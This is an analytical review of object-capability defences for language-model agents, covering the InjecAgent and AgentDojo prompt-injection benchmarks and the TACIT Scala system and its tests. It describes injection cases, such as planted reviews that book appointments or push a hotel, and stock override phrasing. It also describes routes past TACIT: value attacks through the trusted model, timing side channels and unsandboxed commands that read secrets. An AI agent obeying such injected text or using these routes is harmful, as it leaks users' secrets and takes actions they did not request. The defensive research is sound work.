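# Object-capability security for language-model tool use: the systems built and what their tests show

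## Capabilities, confused deputies and prompt injection

Object-capability security is an approach to access control in which a program can act on a resource only if it holds an unforgeable reference to it. The reference both identifies the resource and grants the right to use it. Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn proposed the idea in 1966, and designers of operating systems and programming languages have built on it since. More recently, security researchers have applied it to language-model agents, in which a large language model chooses actions, such as sending an email or paying a bill, and other software carries them out.

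Agents are an obvious candidate for object-capability security because much of the text they process comes from strangers and can change what they do. If an agent holds references only to what its task needs, an attacker who redirects it can do less. How much less depends partly on the mechanism and partly on how it performs under attack.

### How text becomes an action

A language model only produces text. A developer can make it an agent by adding descriptions of functions, called tools, to its prompt. Each description gives the tool's name, purpose and arguments. When the user makes a request, the model can respond with a tool call, which names a tool and gives a value for each argument in an agreed format. The software around the model parses the call, runs the function and adds the result to the model's input. This cycle repeats until the model gives a final answer.

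A tool's result enters the same stream of text as the user's request, and Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) point out in *AgentDojo* that models have no formal way to tell instructions from data in that stream. Anyone who can write text that the agent will read, such as a product review, a shared file or an incoming email, can put instructions there. Researchers call this indirect prompt injection because the attacker leaves text for a tool to fetch instead of addressing the model directly. In an example from *InjecAgent* (Zhan, Liang and colleagues, 2024), a user asks whether a dentist has good reviews on a health app, and one of the reviews is an instruction to book an appointment. If the model responds with a booking call, the tool books an appointment the user didn't request.

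The model outputs a tool call, and the surrounding software carries it out. Ordinarily, that software runs any well-formed call with the logins and keys the user gave the agent at the start. If a stranger's review prompts the agent to book an appointment, the clinic receives the request from the patient's own account, with no record of the review's role. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) calls this kind of permission ambient authority, defined as authority "that is exercised, but not selected, by its user". Its example is the Unix file system. When a program asks to open a file by name, the operating system decides based on the account the program runs under, and the program presents no credential for that particular file. Similarly, every email sent by an agent with a mailbox login carries the full authority of the account, regardless of who prompted it.

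### Capabilities and access-control lists

An access-control list records who may do what with a resource, and is attached to that resource. Unix permissions are a simple example. Textbooks often introduce access-control lists and capabilities as two ways of storing the same table. Each row is a subject (a user or program), each column is a resource, and each cell holds the subject's rights to that resource, such as Alice's right to read the password file. A column is then one resource's access-control list, and a row is one subject's set of capabilities. Access-control lists and capabilities therefore appear to hold the same information, and many people have concluded that they are equivalent.

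Miller and colleagues argue that access-control lists and capabilities are not equivalent, because a table of permissions omits how subjects refer to resources and how the entries change over time. An access-control list is kept with the resource and identifies the subjects allowed to use it. A program must therefore name the resource in some shared vocabulary, such as file paths, and anyone can produce that name, with or without permission to use the resource. A capability is held by the subject and refers to the resource, so a program that can designate the resource already has the right to use it.

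Capability systems can also divide authority more finely than access-control lists. Because somebody has to keep an access-control list up to date, in practice designers tend to use a small, stable set of subjects, usually user accounts. A capability system can treat each running instance of a program as a separate holder. If one person has an agent sorting receipts and another booking flights, a list of accounts doesn't distinguish between them, but in a capability system the receipt agent doesn't need to hold any of the flight agent's capabilities.

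A program in an object-capability system can get a reference to an object in exactly four ways. For example, the software gives an agent a reference to the user's calendar at start-up (initial conditions). The agent creates a draft document and so holds the only reference to it (parenthood). It then creates a helper program to find free dates, with a reference to the calendar built in (endowment). Later, it sends the helper a message containing a reference to the draft (introduction). A program cannot get a reference by guessing an object's name.

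Delegation works by introduction, which requires the sender to already hold references to both the recipient and the object it shares. If no chain of references connects two groups of objects, no capability can pass between them, so a user who distrusts a program can avoid connecting it to anything that matters. Miller and colleagues use this to answer critics' long-standing objection that capabilities spread without control because any holder may pass them on.

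If the agent in the example wants its helper only to read the calendar, it can create an intermediary object that passes on read requests and refuses write requests, and give the helper a reference to that object. Deriving a weaker capability from a stronger one in this way is called attenuation. The agent can also use an intermediary to revoke access. It places a forwarder between the helper and the calendar, keeps control of the forwarder, and later turns forwarding off. The helper still holds its reference, but requests sent through it no longer reach the calendar, and the same is true for anyone to whom the helper passed the reference. David Redell described this revocation scheme in 1974.

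### The compiler that overwrote the bills

The case for capabilities rests heavily on one anecdote. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) recounts an incident from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

1. Administrators installed a compiler in a directory with the name SYSX. They gave it a licence to write files in that directory, so that it could record statistics in a file there, (SYSX)STAT.
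2. The compiler also let its caller name a file for optional debugging output. A user supplied the name (SYSX)BILL, which was the company's billing file.
3. The compiler passed that name to the operating system and asked to open the file for writing.
4. The operating system checked the compiler's licence, found that it covered everything in SYSX, and opened the file.
5. The compiler wrote its debugging output over the billing records.

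The user did not have permission to write to the billing file. The compiler had it for a different purpose, and the user exploited that permission by supplying the file's name. Hardy calls a program a confused deputy when a party without its legitimate authority induces it to misuse that authority.

Hardy considers the obvious repairs and finds a problem with each. The compiler could refuse file names in other directories, but users have good reasons to send output there. It could refuse anything in SYSX, but some callers have legitimate access to SYSX, and the directory did not exist under that name when the programmers wrote the code. It could refuse only (SYSX)BILL, but programmers would then have to amend it whenever someone added another sensitive file. Tymshare added a system call that let a program declare whether it was using its caller's authority or its own, but it soon became clear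 that some programs needed more than two authorities. By Hardy's last count, the rule for opening a file contained fourteen logical operators.

To fix this with capabilities, the administrators give the compiler a reference to the statistics file, and a caller who wants debugging output supplies a reference to the file that should receive it. The compiler writes to each file through its reference and never handles a file name. A caller with no right to the billing file has no reference to it, so they can't pass one to the compiler. UT Austin's *The Confused Deputy*, a set of lecture slides, describes the same solution in Unix, where a launcher with little authority of its own opens the debugging file and gives the compiler a file descriptor, a small number that identifies an open file in a table the operating system keeps for each process.

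File descriptors also suggest how a language model, which can only print text, might use references. The number 3 is not secret and grants nothing by itself; it has an effect only when the operating system looks it up in the calling process's table. Similarly, the model can print a label, and the software around it can look that label up among the references this agent received. An attacker can make the model print any label, but the label has no effect unless it matches one of those references.

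An email tool built this way would accept a reference to a recipient instead of an address. The references would come from the user's request or address book. An address that an attacker planted in a message would be only a string, so the tool would not accept it. Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), a software vendor's blog post, likewise proposes capabilities as the answer to confused deputies on the web of agents.

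### Misuse of a reference rightly held

Hardy's compiler is an imperfect analogy for an agent. The compiler followed its code, and its caller could choose little more than a file name, while text in an agent's context can affect which tools the model calls, with which arguments and in which order. An attacker may therefore not need to name a forbidden resource if misusing a permitted one is enough.

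Rajani, Garg and Rezk (2016), in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, worked out formally how much this matters. They model a program as a sequence of commands that run with different levels of authority, one of them the attacker's. Their definition counts the program as free of confused-deputy attacks if, for every memory location *r* that the attacker wants to change, at least one of two conditions holds:

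- the final value in *r* is the same whatever commands the attacker runs; or
- the attacker could have written that final value to *r* directly.

Under this definition, a confused deputy attack requires that the attacker influence the result and need the deputy to do so. Capabilities stop the compiler attack but not the following one. Suppose the attacker may write to location *r′* but not to *r*, and the deputy, which may write to both, runs a single command that copies the contents of *r′* into *r*. If the attacker stores 42 in *r′*, then *r* ends with 42, and if the attacker stores 41, *r* ends with 41. The attacker has determined the contents of *r* and needed the deputy to do it, so this counts as an attack, even though the deputy used its own legitimate reference to *r* and the attacker never designated *r*. Rajani and colleagues call this a value attack and compare it to SQL injection,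 in which a web server with legitimate access to a database writes something hostile into it.

They also prove that capabilities suffice if neither the deputy's code nor the initial memory contains references to the locations that need protection. They concede that this condition makes the language useless for almost all practical purposes. It protects those locations by leaving the deputy with no authority of its own, which a deputy normally needs to do its job.

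Their alternative is to track provenance by labeling each value with the least trusted source that contributed to it, and to block a write when the label is too low for the destination. The version with less overhead follows only direct copying, so it misses influence through branches, as when a program writes 41 or 42 depending on a yes-or-no value from the attacker. The full version also tracks branches and prevents every confused-deputy attack in their model. Some influence is legitimate. For example, the compiler's bill should depend on the size of the user's source file. The programmer can therefore exempt a piece of code by marking it as endorsed.

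Labeling arguments by the trustworthiness of their sources is difficult with a language model, because its output can depend on anything in its context. Strict labeling would require giving every argument the model produces the label of the least trustworthy text it has processed. Debenedetti and colleagues describe an attack that no capability reference can prevent. A user asks for a hotel recommendation, and one hotel's listing contains an instruction to always recommend that hotel. The agent gives the user the attacker's recommendation without calling a forbidden tool or contacting a stranger.

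### Four meanings of one word

Habitat Chronicles (2017), a practitioners' blog, warns readers not to be misled by the word "capabilities". The word has at least four meanings in work on agents, and "capability-based" may refer to any of three of these when it describes a system.

In the strict sense, a capability is an object reference that a program can obtain only in the four ways above. Only such a reference is an object capability, and typed agent code can hold one in an ordinary variable.

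A signed token is similar to an object capability but lacks some of its properties. The issuer writes down a resource and a permitted action, then signs the text cryptographically so that nobody can forge or alter it. AgentCap uses one such token for each tool call. Miller and colleagues discuss an older scheme of this kind, SPKI certificates, and compare them to keys. The bearer must select and present a certificate, so the authority is not ambient. But the bearer can copy it to anyone, even without a prior connection, and it names the resource in plain text, so the name can be separated from the right to use the resource. Such a token can still prevent a confused deputy if it arrives with the request it belongs to and the recipient keeps track of what it is for.

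Many agent frameworks use "capability", or a similar term, for a tool on a permitted list. Capability gating decides whether an agent may call a tool such as `send_email` without looking at the arguments of each call. Per-call authorization checks each proposed call together with its arguments, and so stops different things. Permitted lists have a precedent in POSIX "capabilities", a fixed set of flags in Unix-like systems. One flag lets a process change the ownership of any file on the machine. Miller and colleagues object that a fixed set of flags cannot express rights over individual files, which users create and delete all the time. Permission to call `send_email` has the same defect, because it covers every recipient and any content.

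Finally, AI researchers use "capability" to mean what a model is able to do. *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition*, a post by the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), uses "model capability" in this sense. Because this sense has nothing to do with permission, the text below uses "skill" for it instead.

### InjecAgent and AgentDojo

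Researchers usually test defences against indirect prompt injection on benchmarks, and two from 2024 have been influential.

Zhan and colleagues built InjecAgent by pairing each of 17 user requests with each of 62 attacker instructions, which gives 1,054 tests. Every request makes the agent fetch outside content, which contains the attacker's instruction. Thirty of the instructions do direct harm, such as unlocking a front door, and 32 steal data and email it to the attacker. The base setting uses the instruction alone, while the enhanced setting adds a stock phrase before it that tells the model to ignore everything it has read so far. Each test begins after the agent has correctly fetched the content. A direct-harm attack succeeds if the agent then calls the harmful tool. A theft succeeds if the agent retrieves the data and then sends it, with GPT-4 simulating the retrieval tool's reply.

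The main score is the attack success rate, the share of attacked trials in which the attacker reaches the goal. Zhan and colleagues exclude malformed outputs when they compute it. GPT-4, prompted to act as an agent, had a rate of 23.6% in base cases and 47.0% in enhanced ones. A version of GPT-4 trained to make function calls had rates of 6.6% and 7.1%. Claude 2's rate fell from 11.4% to 3.4%, perhaps because the stock phrase made the attack easier for it to detect. These models are long out of date. Zhan and colleagues acknowledge that each test covers a single exchange, that attacks have at most two steps, and that the fetched content consists entirely of the attacker's instruction. The attack success rate also does not measure whether the agent finished the user's task.

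AgentDojo, by Debenedetti and colleagues, tests agents against prompt injection in four simulated workplaces with working tools. The agent has to plan and carry out a whole task in one workplace, where an email, web page or file contains the attacker's text. The benchmark pairs every user task with every attacker goal in the same workplace.

| Suite | Tools | User tasks | Attacker's goals | Pairs |
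|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack (team messages, web pages) | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel (bookings) | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 74 | 97 | 27 | 629 |

After each run, ordinary code checks the state of the simulated world, such as whether money moved or an email was sent. The designers avoided using a language model as judge because an injection that hijacks the agent might also hijack the judge. They report three numbers. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when there is no attack. Utility under attack is the share of pairs of user task and attacker's goal in which the agent completes the user's task without harmful side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of pairs in which the attacker's goal is achieved.

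The standard attack is written as an important message that addresses the model and the user by name and asks the model to do the attacker's task before anything else. Against GPT-4o, the attack succeeded in 45.8% of cases with neither name, 47.7% with the correct names, and about 23% with a wrong name.

One defence in the original paper is a tool filter, the simplest form of capability gating. Before the agent fetches any data, the model picks the tools that the user's request calls for, and the software withholds the rest. The filter reduced attack success to 7.5%, largely because many of the user tasks only read data while the attacks need to write. It does not help when the tools needed for the task are also enough for the attack, as in 17% of the test cases. It also struggles when the agent cannot know in advance which tools it will need. If an agent keeps its context between tasks,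 an attacker could inject an instruction to wait for a later task that provides the tools the attack needs.

Some AgentDojo tests are flawed because the injected text replaces information that the user's task requires. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) shows a request to pay a bill in which the attack has overwritten the bill's contents. No agent could complete that task, so low utility under attack may be due to the benchmark as well as the defence. *AgentDojo-Inspect*, a version maintained by the US standards agency NIST, fixes bugs, drops poor tasks and adds new attacks. AgentDojo has also grown to over 900 pairs, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026). It remains in use alongside a newer benchmark, AgentDyn. *StepGuard* (2026) describes AgentDyn as having longer workflows, in settings that include shopping and GitHub, and third-party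 instructions that are sometimes helpful. These helpful instructions matter because a defence can do well on AgentDojo by ignoring every instruction it finds in data.

### Fixed attacks and adapted ones

Both benchmarks include ready-made attack texts, and much of the published evidence relies on them. Debenedetti and colleagues themselves thought this unsatisfactory, since it is extremely easy to build a defence that stops one particular attack. For example, repeating the user's request after each tool result works well against their "important message" attack, but would probably fail against an injection that tells the model to disregard future instructions.

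CAISI's *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, first published in January 2025, reports that its staff and the UK AI Security Institute wrote new attacks specifically for a version of Claude 3.5 Sonnet that resisted existing ones well. They developed the attacks on some of the Workspace tasks and measured them on others. The best new attack succeeded 81% of the time, compared with 11% for the best existing attack. The new attacks also worked on the other three suites.

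Repeated attempts also help the attacker. On a set of five attacker's goals, making 25 attempts at each raised the average success rate from 57% to 80%. If every attempt at every goal had an independent 57% chance of success, practically all the goals would have been achieved, so the average evidently includes some that the agent almost never carries out. Success rates therefore depend on whether they count attempts or cases. In the later public competition that CAISI describes, more than 400 people made over 250,000 attempts against 13 leading models and found at least one successful attack on each.

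*AutoDojo* (2026) tests defences with a program that generates injections tailored to each agent and defence. Across ten defences, five models and six task suites, fixed attacks often made defences look considerably better than they were, because a defence can learn to recognise the wording of well-known injections without detecting malicious intent in general.

In principle, rewording an injection does not help an attacker get past a capability check, because the check compares each call with a set of rights and never processes the attacker's text. An attacker who adapts will instead try to get a permitted tool called with a harmful argument, or exploit a step at which the model itself decides which rights to grant. A test with stock injections may miss both attacks. It would be more informative to assume that the model already obeys the attacker and test which calls still go through.

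Whether capabilities protect an agent depends partly on who grants the authority and on the basis of what text. An injection can influence the grant if a model makes it after reading the attacker's email, but not if the user makes it beforehand. Protection also depends on whether the reference itself carries the right, or only names something that the software opens using a standing permission, as the operating system opened the billing file under the compiler's licence. The strength of the evidence depends on what the testers attacked and whether they adapted the attack to the defence or used an existing one. It also depends on how much the defence reduces the agent's usefulness, because an agent that refuses every tool call has an attack success rate of zero.

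## TACIT: checking an agent's code before it runs

With TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), an agent writes short programs in Scala 3 instead of making separate tool calls. Before a program runs, the Scala compiler works out which capabilities the program could use, and rejects the whole program if it uses one where the types don't allow it. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues built the system at EPFL in Lausanne and present it in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026).

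TACIT runs as a server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect agents to tools, so existing coding agents can use it. The agent sends its program to the server in a tool call. If the program doesn't compile, the agent receives the error message and can try again. Otherwise the server runs the program in an interactive session, which keeps variables from one program to the next. Programs are supposed to reach files, other processes and the network only through a library that comes with TACIT.

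A coding assistant may work on a project that has a folder of API keys. If its model runs on another company's servers, a key leaves the user's control once it enters the model's context. A permission list can allow the agent to read project files and to contact its model, but it doesn't cover the combination of reading a key and then sending it out. Odersky and colleagues argue that a sandbox has the same gap, because it permits both steps. They designed TACIT to catch the flow of data from one permitted step to the next.

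### Capture sets

In a typed language, a value's type identifies it to the compiler as, for example, a number, a piece of text, or a function that turns text into a number. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, adds to the type a list of the capabilities the value can reach, called the value's capture set.

Suppose `f` is an open file and `log` is a function that takes a message and writes it to `f`. Without capture checking, the type of `log` is `String -> Unit`, which means that it takes text and returns no useful value. With capture checking, the type becomes `String ->{f} Unit`, where the capture set `{f}` shows that calling `log` may use `f`. A function with an empty capture set is pure, so it can compute a result from its input but can't write a file, send a message or do anything else that needs a capability.

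The compiler lets a value with a smaller capture set stand in for one with a larger set, and never the reverse. In Scala's notation, where `<:` means "may be used as", the rule for a type `A` and capabilities `f` and `g` is:

`A <: A^{f} <: A^{f, g} <: A^`

The last form, `A^`, permits any capabilities. A pure function can therefore be used anywhere, while `log` can be used only where the expected type allows `f`. A capture set may include a capability that a particular run never uses, so the compiler sometimes rejects a harmless program.

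Older object-capability languages, such as E and Joe-E, control references while a program runs. They can stop a program from using a reference it doesn't have, but their types don't show that a given function holds no references. TACIT needs that guarantee to protect secrets. Its compiler can establish that one part of a program has no side effects while leaving the rest free to have them, which Odersky and colleagues call local purity.

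### A file system confined to a block

A program gets file access by calling `requestFileSystem` with the name of a root directory and a block of code. The library creates a capability for that directory and everything under it, passes it to the block, and invalidates it when the block ends. Inside the block, the program can call `access("README.md")` to get a handle for one file. The handle's type records that it depends on the file-system capability. If the program requests a path outside the root, the library blocks the request with an error at run time.

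A program might try to keep its access by returning a function that reads the file later. In most languages this would work, because the function would still hold the reference. In TACIT, the function's type has to list the file-system capability in its capture set. That capability has a name only inside the block, so the type of the block's result can't refer to it, and the compiler rejects the program. Storing a file handle in a variable outside the block fails for the same reason. During the experiments, one agent tried to return a list of file handles from its block and got a compiler error. TACIT therefore keeps the reference from leaving the block, while Redell's forwarder disables a reference that the program still holds.

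### The Classified wrapper

When a program reads a file on a protected path, the library returns a `Classified[String]` instead of an ordinary string. This is a sealed container. The program can store it and pass it around, but opening it requires a capability that the agent doesn't have. To work on the contents, the program gives a function to the container's `map` method, which applies the function inside and seals the result in a new container. The following program compiles:

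```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
  val size = key.map(k => k.length)
  println(size)      // the agent sees Classified(****)
}
```

The function that computes the length captures nothing, so `map` accepts it. Printing the result is harmless because a `Classified` container always converts to the same masked text. The next program tries to copy the key into an ordinary file:

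```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
  val notes = access("notes.txt")
  key.map { k =>
    notes.write(k)   // error: this function captures notes
    k
  }
}
```

The function now has the type `String ->{notes} String`, but `map` requires a function with an empty capture set. The compiler reports the mismatch, and the server runs none of the program. Calling `println` inside `map` also fails, because printing needs an input/output capability. Calling `requestFileSystem` there fails too, so a program can't get around the rule by opening a new file system inside the function.

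Summarising a sealed incident report takes more than arithmetic, so the library offers a `chat` function that passes sealed text to a second language model. This model has no tools, and the operator trusts it with secrets, perhaps because it runs on the operator's own machine. Its answer comes back sealed, so the agent can request a summary and save it to a protected file without its own model seeing the report or the summary. Simon Willison proposed this division of labour between two models in 2023, and TACIT adds types that control what passes between them.

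### Two output channels

The agent's model and the user both need the output of the agent's programs, but only the user may read the secrets in it. TACIT therefore sends printed text through two channels. The normal channel goes into the model's context, with `Classified(****)` in place of any sealed value. The secure channel gives the user the same text with the real contents shown.

Odersky and colleagues give an example in which a user asks for a summary of a confidential contract. The agent obtains the summary through the trusted model and prints it. The user sees the text, while the agent's model receives only the mask. In the next turn, the user asks how long the summary is. The file-system capability from the first turn has expired, but the variable holding the summary still exists in the session and is still sealed. The agent applies a length function to it and prints the result,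 which again only the user sees.

Keeping secrets out of the agent's model's context also keeps the protected text from influencing that model. If an attacker has planted an instruction in the contract, only the trusted model reads it, and that model can only return text. An instruction in a file the operator has left unclassified, such as the project's README, still reaches the agent's model and can change what it writes next.

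### What the guarantee depends on

Odersky and colleagues treat the agent as an adversary. Their guarantee is supposed to hold whether the agent's model makes a mistake, follows an injected instruction or deliberately tries to steal a key. Everything that enforces the rules has to be trustworthy, including the compiler, the software that runs the compiled program, the library and the second model, which must not carry a secret from one query into another. The operator also has to mark the right files as protected.

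The agent must have no way to act except through TACIT. The EPFL group's GitHub page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, advises users to switch off their coding agent's built-in tools for files, shell commands and the network. An agent that keeps its ordinary shell could read the API keys without sending any Scala code to TACIT.

Scala has features that would break the guarantee. For example, a type cast can tell the compiler to treat a function that captures a file as if it were pure. *Safe Mode*, part of Scala's documentation, describes a subset of the language for code written by agents. The subset bans unchecked casts and pattern matches, features explicitly marked as unsafe, annotations that turn off checks, and reflection, which lets a program inspect and call parts of itself by name. It also requires capture checking and allows calls only to global code that is itself safe.

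Library programmers often need the features that safe mode bans. They can exempt their code with the annotation `@assumeSafe`, but then they must make sure themselves that the code is safe. Scala's example is an email function that asks the user to confirm each message and then calls an unrestricted mailer. If the programmer forgot the confirmation, the compiler would still accept the agent's calls. Errors are another gap, because a program could put a secret into an error message, and tracking every possible error in the types would be impractical. TACIT instead catches errors while the program runs and hides their details.

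The theory behind capture checking is further along than the software. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) contains a proof of type safety for an extended version of its formal core, checked in the proof assistant Lean 4. The proof covers a small mathematical language, and Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode still needs its own soundness argument. Scala's documentation describes capture checking as "highly experimental and unstable".

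When lampepfl first published the safety test results, the server enforced safe mode with a validator that searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns. Such a search finds only the patterns its programmers thought of. Glama's *TACIT*, a later copy of the project's documentation in a directory of MCP servers, lists the compiler's own safe mode as on by default, in addition to the validator.

### Names and references in TACIT

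A file handle inside a block is an object capability in the strict sense. But TACIT relaxes the classical model in one respect. It allows global capabilities, which any code can mention. Odersky and colleagues consider this safe because a function's capture set must include any global capability the function uses.

The way a program obtains its first handle is a larger departure. `requestFileSystem` takes a directory name, and the equivalent functions for the network and for other processes take lists of host names and commands. The agent's program supplies these names, using an input/output capability available throughout the session, so in effect the agent grants itself access. Capture checking ensures that the resulting capability stays inside its block, but it doesn't check whether the agent should have asked for that directory or host.

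The later version lets an operator set outer limits, which matter as much as the type system if an agent is hijacked. According to Glama, a requested directory must be inside a permitted one, by default the server's working directory. The operator can also list allowed hosts and commands, and a program can use only those that are both on the operator's list and in its own request. If the operator lists no hosts, only the agent's request limits which hosts the program can use.

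The tools in the experiments also depend on names. `cancelReservation` takes a reservation number and `sendMoney` takes a recipient, both as strings. An agent that can call either function can supply any number or recipient, so the types alone don't keep these tools from becoming confused deputies.

### The leak test

Odersky and colleagues tested the protection of secrets on a small software project with a `secret` directory that held API keys, a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 legitimate user tasks. Some were routine, such as listing the functions described in a README, and others involved protected data, such as anonymizing employee reviews. They also hid 10 injections in the project's files. The simplest were instructions in code comments. More elaborate ones imitated system messages, faked an error that supposedly required a password to fix, claimed that the secrets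 were only test data, or included ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets.

Running each task with each injection gave 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the malicious request came from the user instead of an injection. Five of these requests asked for secrets outright, and six used a pretext, such as an administrator's emergency. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output. Two models went through all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in `Classified` containers and once with them as plain strings.

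| Model | Trials | Leaks without the wrapper | Leaks with the wrapper |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 2 | 0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 3 | 0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 8 | 0 |

Odersky and colleagues credit the type system with blocking every attack in the protected runs, but this is hard to accept for the injections, given the results of the unprotected runs. Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted all 120 injections without protection, so the wrapper could not improve its result. MiniMax M2.5 leaked in three of its 120 unprotected trials, which is weak evidence that the wrapper helped. If three leaks fell at random among MiniMax's 240 injection trials, all three would land in the unprotected half about one time in eight. The injections were also a fixed set, and nobody revised them after seeing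 how TACIT responded.

The malicious requests are more informative, although there are only 11 of them. MiniMax complied and leaked secrets in eight when it could read them, but in none when they were sealed. These trials come close to testing a model that already obeys the attacker. In these experiments, the compiler rejected, for example, an agent's attempt to print a GitHub key from inside `map` and another attempt to write confidential recommendations to an open file.

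The wrapper did not make the agents less useful in this test. Claude Sonnet 4.6 gave a correct response in 99.2% of the 120 injection trials with the wrapper and 83.3% without it. MiniMax's rates were 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues suggest that, without the wrapper, Claude often ran out of turns or time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task. Claude's higher rate with the wrapper therefore doesn't show that sealing secrets improves an agent's work.

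### AgentDojo and the comparison with CaMeL

Odersky and colleagues also adapted AgentDojo, the benchmark of simulated workplaces, to TACIT. They kept its user tasks and attacks and rewrote its tools as Scala functions. They then compared their results with published results for another defence, CaMeL, on the same two models. The description of CaMeL here comes only from their paper. CaMeL uses a custom interpreter for a subset of Python to track which data is untrusted while a program runs. One model plans the task and another extracts information from untrusted text, whereas TACIT leaves a single agent in charge.

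TACIT and CaMeL each had one attack counted as successful in 963 trials with o4-mini-high, and none in 963 with Gemini 2.5 Pro. The successful attack was in Travel for TACIT and in Banking for CaMeL. The comparison includes no undefended runs, so it doesn't show how many attacks these models would have resisted without either system.

In TACIT's one failure, the user asked the agent to book a certain hotel, but an attacker had planted a recommendation for a different one in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews word for word, including the planted recommendation. AgentDojo's check found the other hotel's name and counted the attack as a success. Odersky and colleagues object that the check only matches text, and that TACIT's policy permits public reviews to reach the user. They are right that the agent did what the user asked, but the attacker's advertisement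 still reached the user.

Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's utility as "within a range comparable to CaMeL". The figures support this only in part:

| Suite | o4-mini-high, CaMeL | o4-mini-high, TACIT | Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 62.5% | 59.0% | 52.8% | 56.9% |
| Workspace | 81.4% | 52.9% | 53.8% | 50.5% |
| Slack | 68.6% | 47.6% | 48.6% | 40.0% |
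| Travel | 74.3% | 68.6% | 1.4% | 64.3% |

With o4-mini-high, TACIT falls 28.5 percentage points behind CaMeL on Workspace and 21 points behind on Slack. These gaps are too large to call the two systems comparable for office work. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, the results are much closer except on Travel, where CaMeL completed almost no tasks and TACIT did far better. TACIT's percentages correspond to counts of attacked trials (its Banking result with Gemini is 82 of 144), so some of its failures may come from injections that overwrote information the task needed.

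The amount of sealed data may explain why TACIT did worse on Workspace and Slack. In the Travel suite, an agent can read hotel names, prices and opening hours directly, and only text such as reviews and calendar entries is sealed. In Slack, the list of channels is sealed too, and in Workspace, all emails, files and calendar entries are. An agent that can't read this data has to write a program that will work whatever the data contains. If the program fails inside `map`, the error message is also hidden, and the user may get an empty answer.

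The AgentDojo version also seems to relax TACIT's central rule, that a function passed to `map` must be pure. To pay a bill, an agent has to use the account number in the bill, which arrives sealed. The agents' instructions say that side effects inside a `map` function happen immediately, and advise putting "commits" exactly where they should happen. This suggests that agents could send money from inside `map`. The published signature of `sendMoney` doesn't mention a capability either. If agents could do this, the low attack rates in this experiment were due mainly to hiding the injected text from the agent's model, and capture checking contributed little.

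An attacker who knew this could ignore the agent's model and target the second one. The instructions recommend using the second model to extract details such as email addresses from sealed text. An account number planted in a bill could pass through that model and become the recipient of a payment. The agent would have written the program the user wanted, but the attacker would have supplied one of its values. Rajani and colleagues' value attack has the same form. AgentDojo's stock injections are mostly attempts to give the agent a new task, so they are a poor test of this weakness.

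### Performance on ordinary tasks

Models are trained on far less Scala with capture checking than Python or ordinary tool calls. To test whether this makes agents perform worse, Odersky and colleagues ran two benchmarks that contain no attacks. One was τ²-bench, in which an agent helps simulated customers of an airline or a shop. The researchers tested three models and averaged ten runs of each task. The Scala version did slightly better than ordinary tool calls in all six comparisons. The smallest gain was 0.8 percentage points, for DeepSeek V3.2 on airline tasks, and the largest was 3.7 points, for gpt-oss-120b on shop tasks (from 53.3% to 57.0%). Odersky and colleagues think structured results and compiler errors gave the models clearer feedback.

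In SWE-bench Lite, an agent tries to fix 300 real software bugs. MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% with its usual tools, a difference of five bugs. The two benchmarks show that models can write typed Scala about as well as they can make tool calls. They are weaker evidence of how much protecting secrets lowers performance, because the airline and shop tools return ordinary data, without the containers that an agent on AgentDojo had to work around.

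On τ²-bench, between 0.32% and 7.93% of programs needed a retry, depending on the model and the domain. Programs that failed once usually compiled after one or two further attempts. Many of the errors were unrelated to security, such as failing to handle a value that might be missing, or writing a dollar sign in a price without the extra symbol that Scala requires. Checking a typical program takes less than a second, so most of the time spent on a retry goes to running the model again. Capture checking is a small part of that second. *What's in the Box* (2025), which used Scala's standard library as a test case, puts it at under 15% of compilation time.

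The same group extended the approach in *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), which lets a program call a model at any point and state the type of result it needs. The model responds with code, which the compiler checks against the variables and capabilities available at that point. The compiler checks the whole piece of code before any of it runs, so rejected code has no effect. In one example, the model's code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects the code, and the balance stays at 100. LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks on τ²-bench, about as many as the ordinary agent used for comparison. Zhao and colleagues aim to limit what a model can do once an injection has influenced it, and don't claim to prevent the influence itself.

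### Harm within the rules

TACIT does not cover side channels. An agent could write a pure function that runs for a long time if the first bit of a key is 1 and finishes at once if it is 0. The compiler would accept the function, and anyone who could time it would learn that bit. By repeating this for each bit, they could learn the whole key.

Commands that the agent starts outside Scala are a more practical worry, because capture checking doesn't apply to them. Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox where security is critical. A sample configuration in Glama's copy permits `scala`, `java` and `make`, all of which can run code the agent has written to a file. Unless a sandbox prevented it, such code could read the secrets with the user's permissions and print them as plain text.

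An agent can also do damage without learning any secret. The library lets programs seal any value and write it to a protected file, so an agent could overwrite the list of keys that may log in to the user's machine. The current documentation warns that the `Classified` mechanism "protects confidentiality, not integrity" and describes a setting, off by default, that makes protected files read-only. The leak test would not have detected such an attack because it checked only for secrets in the agent's output.

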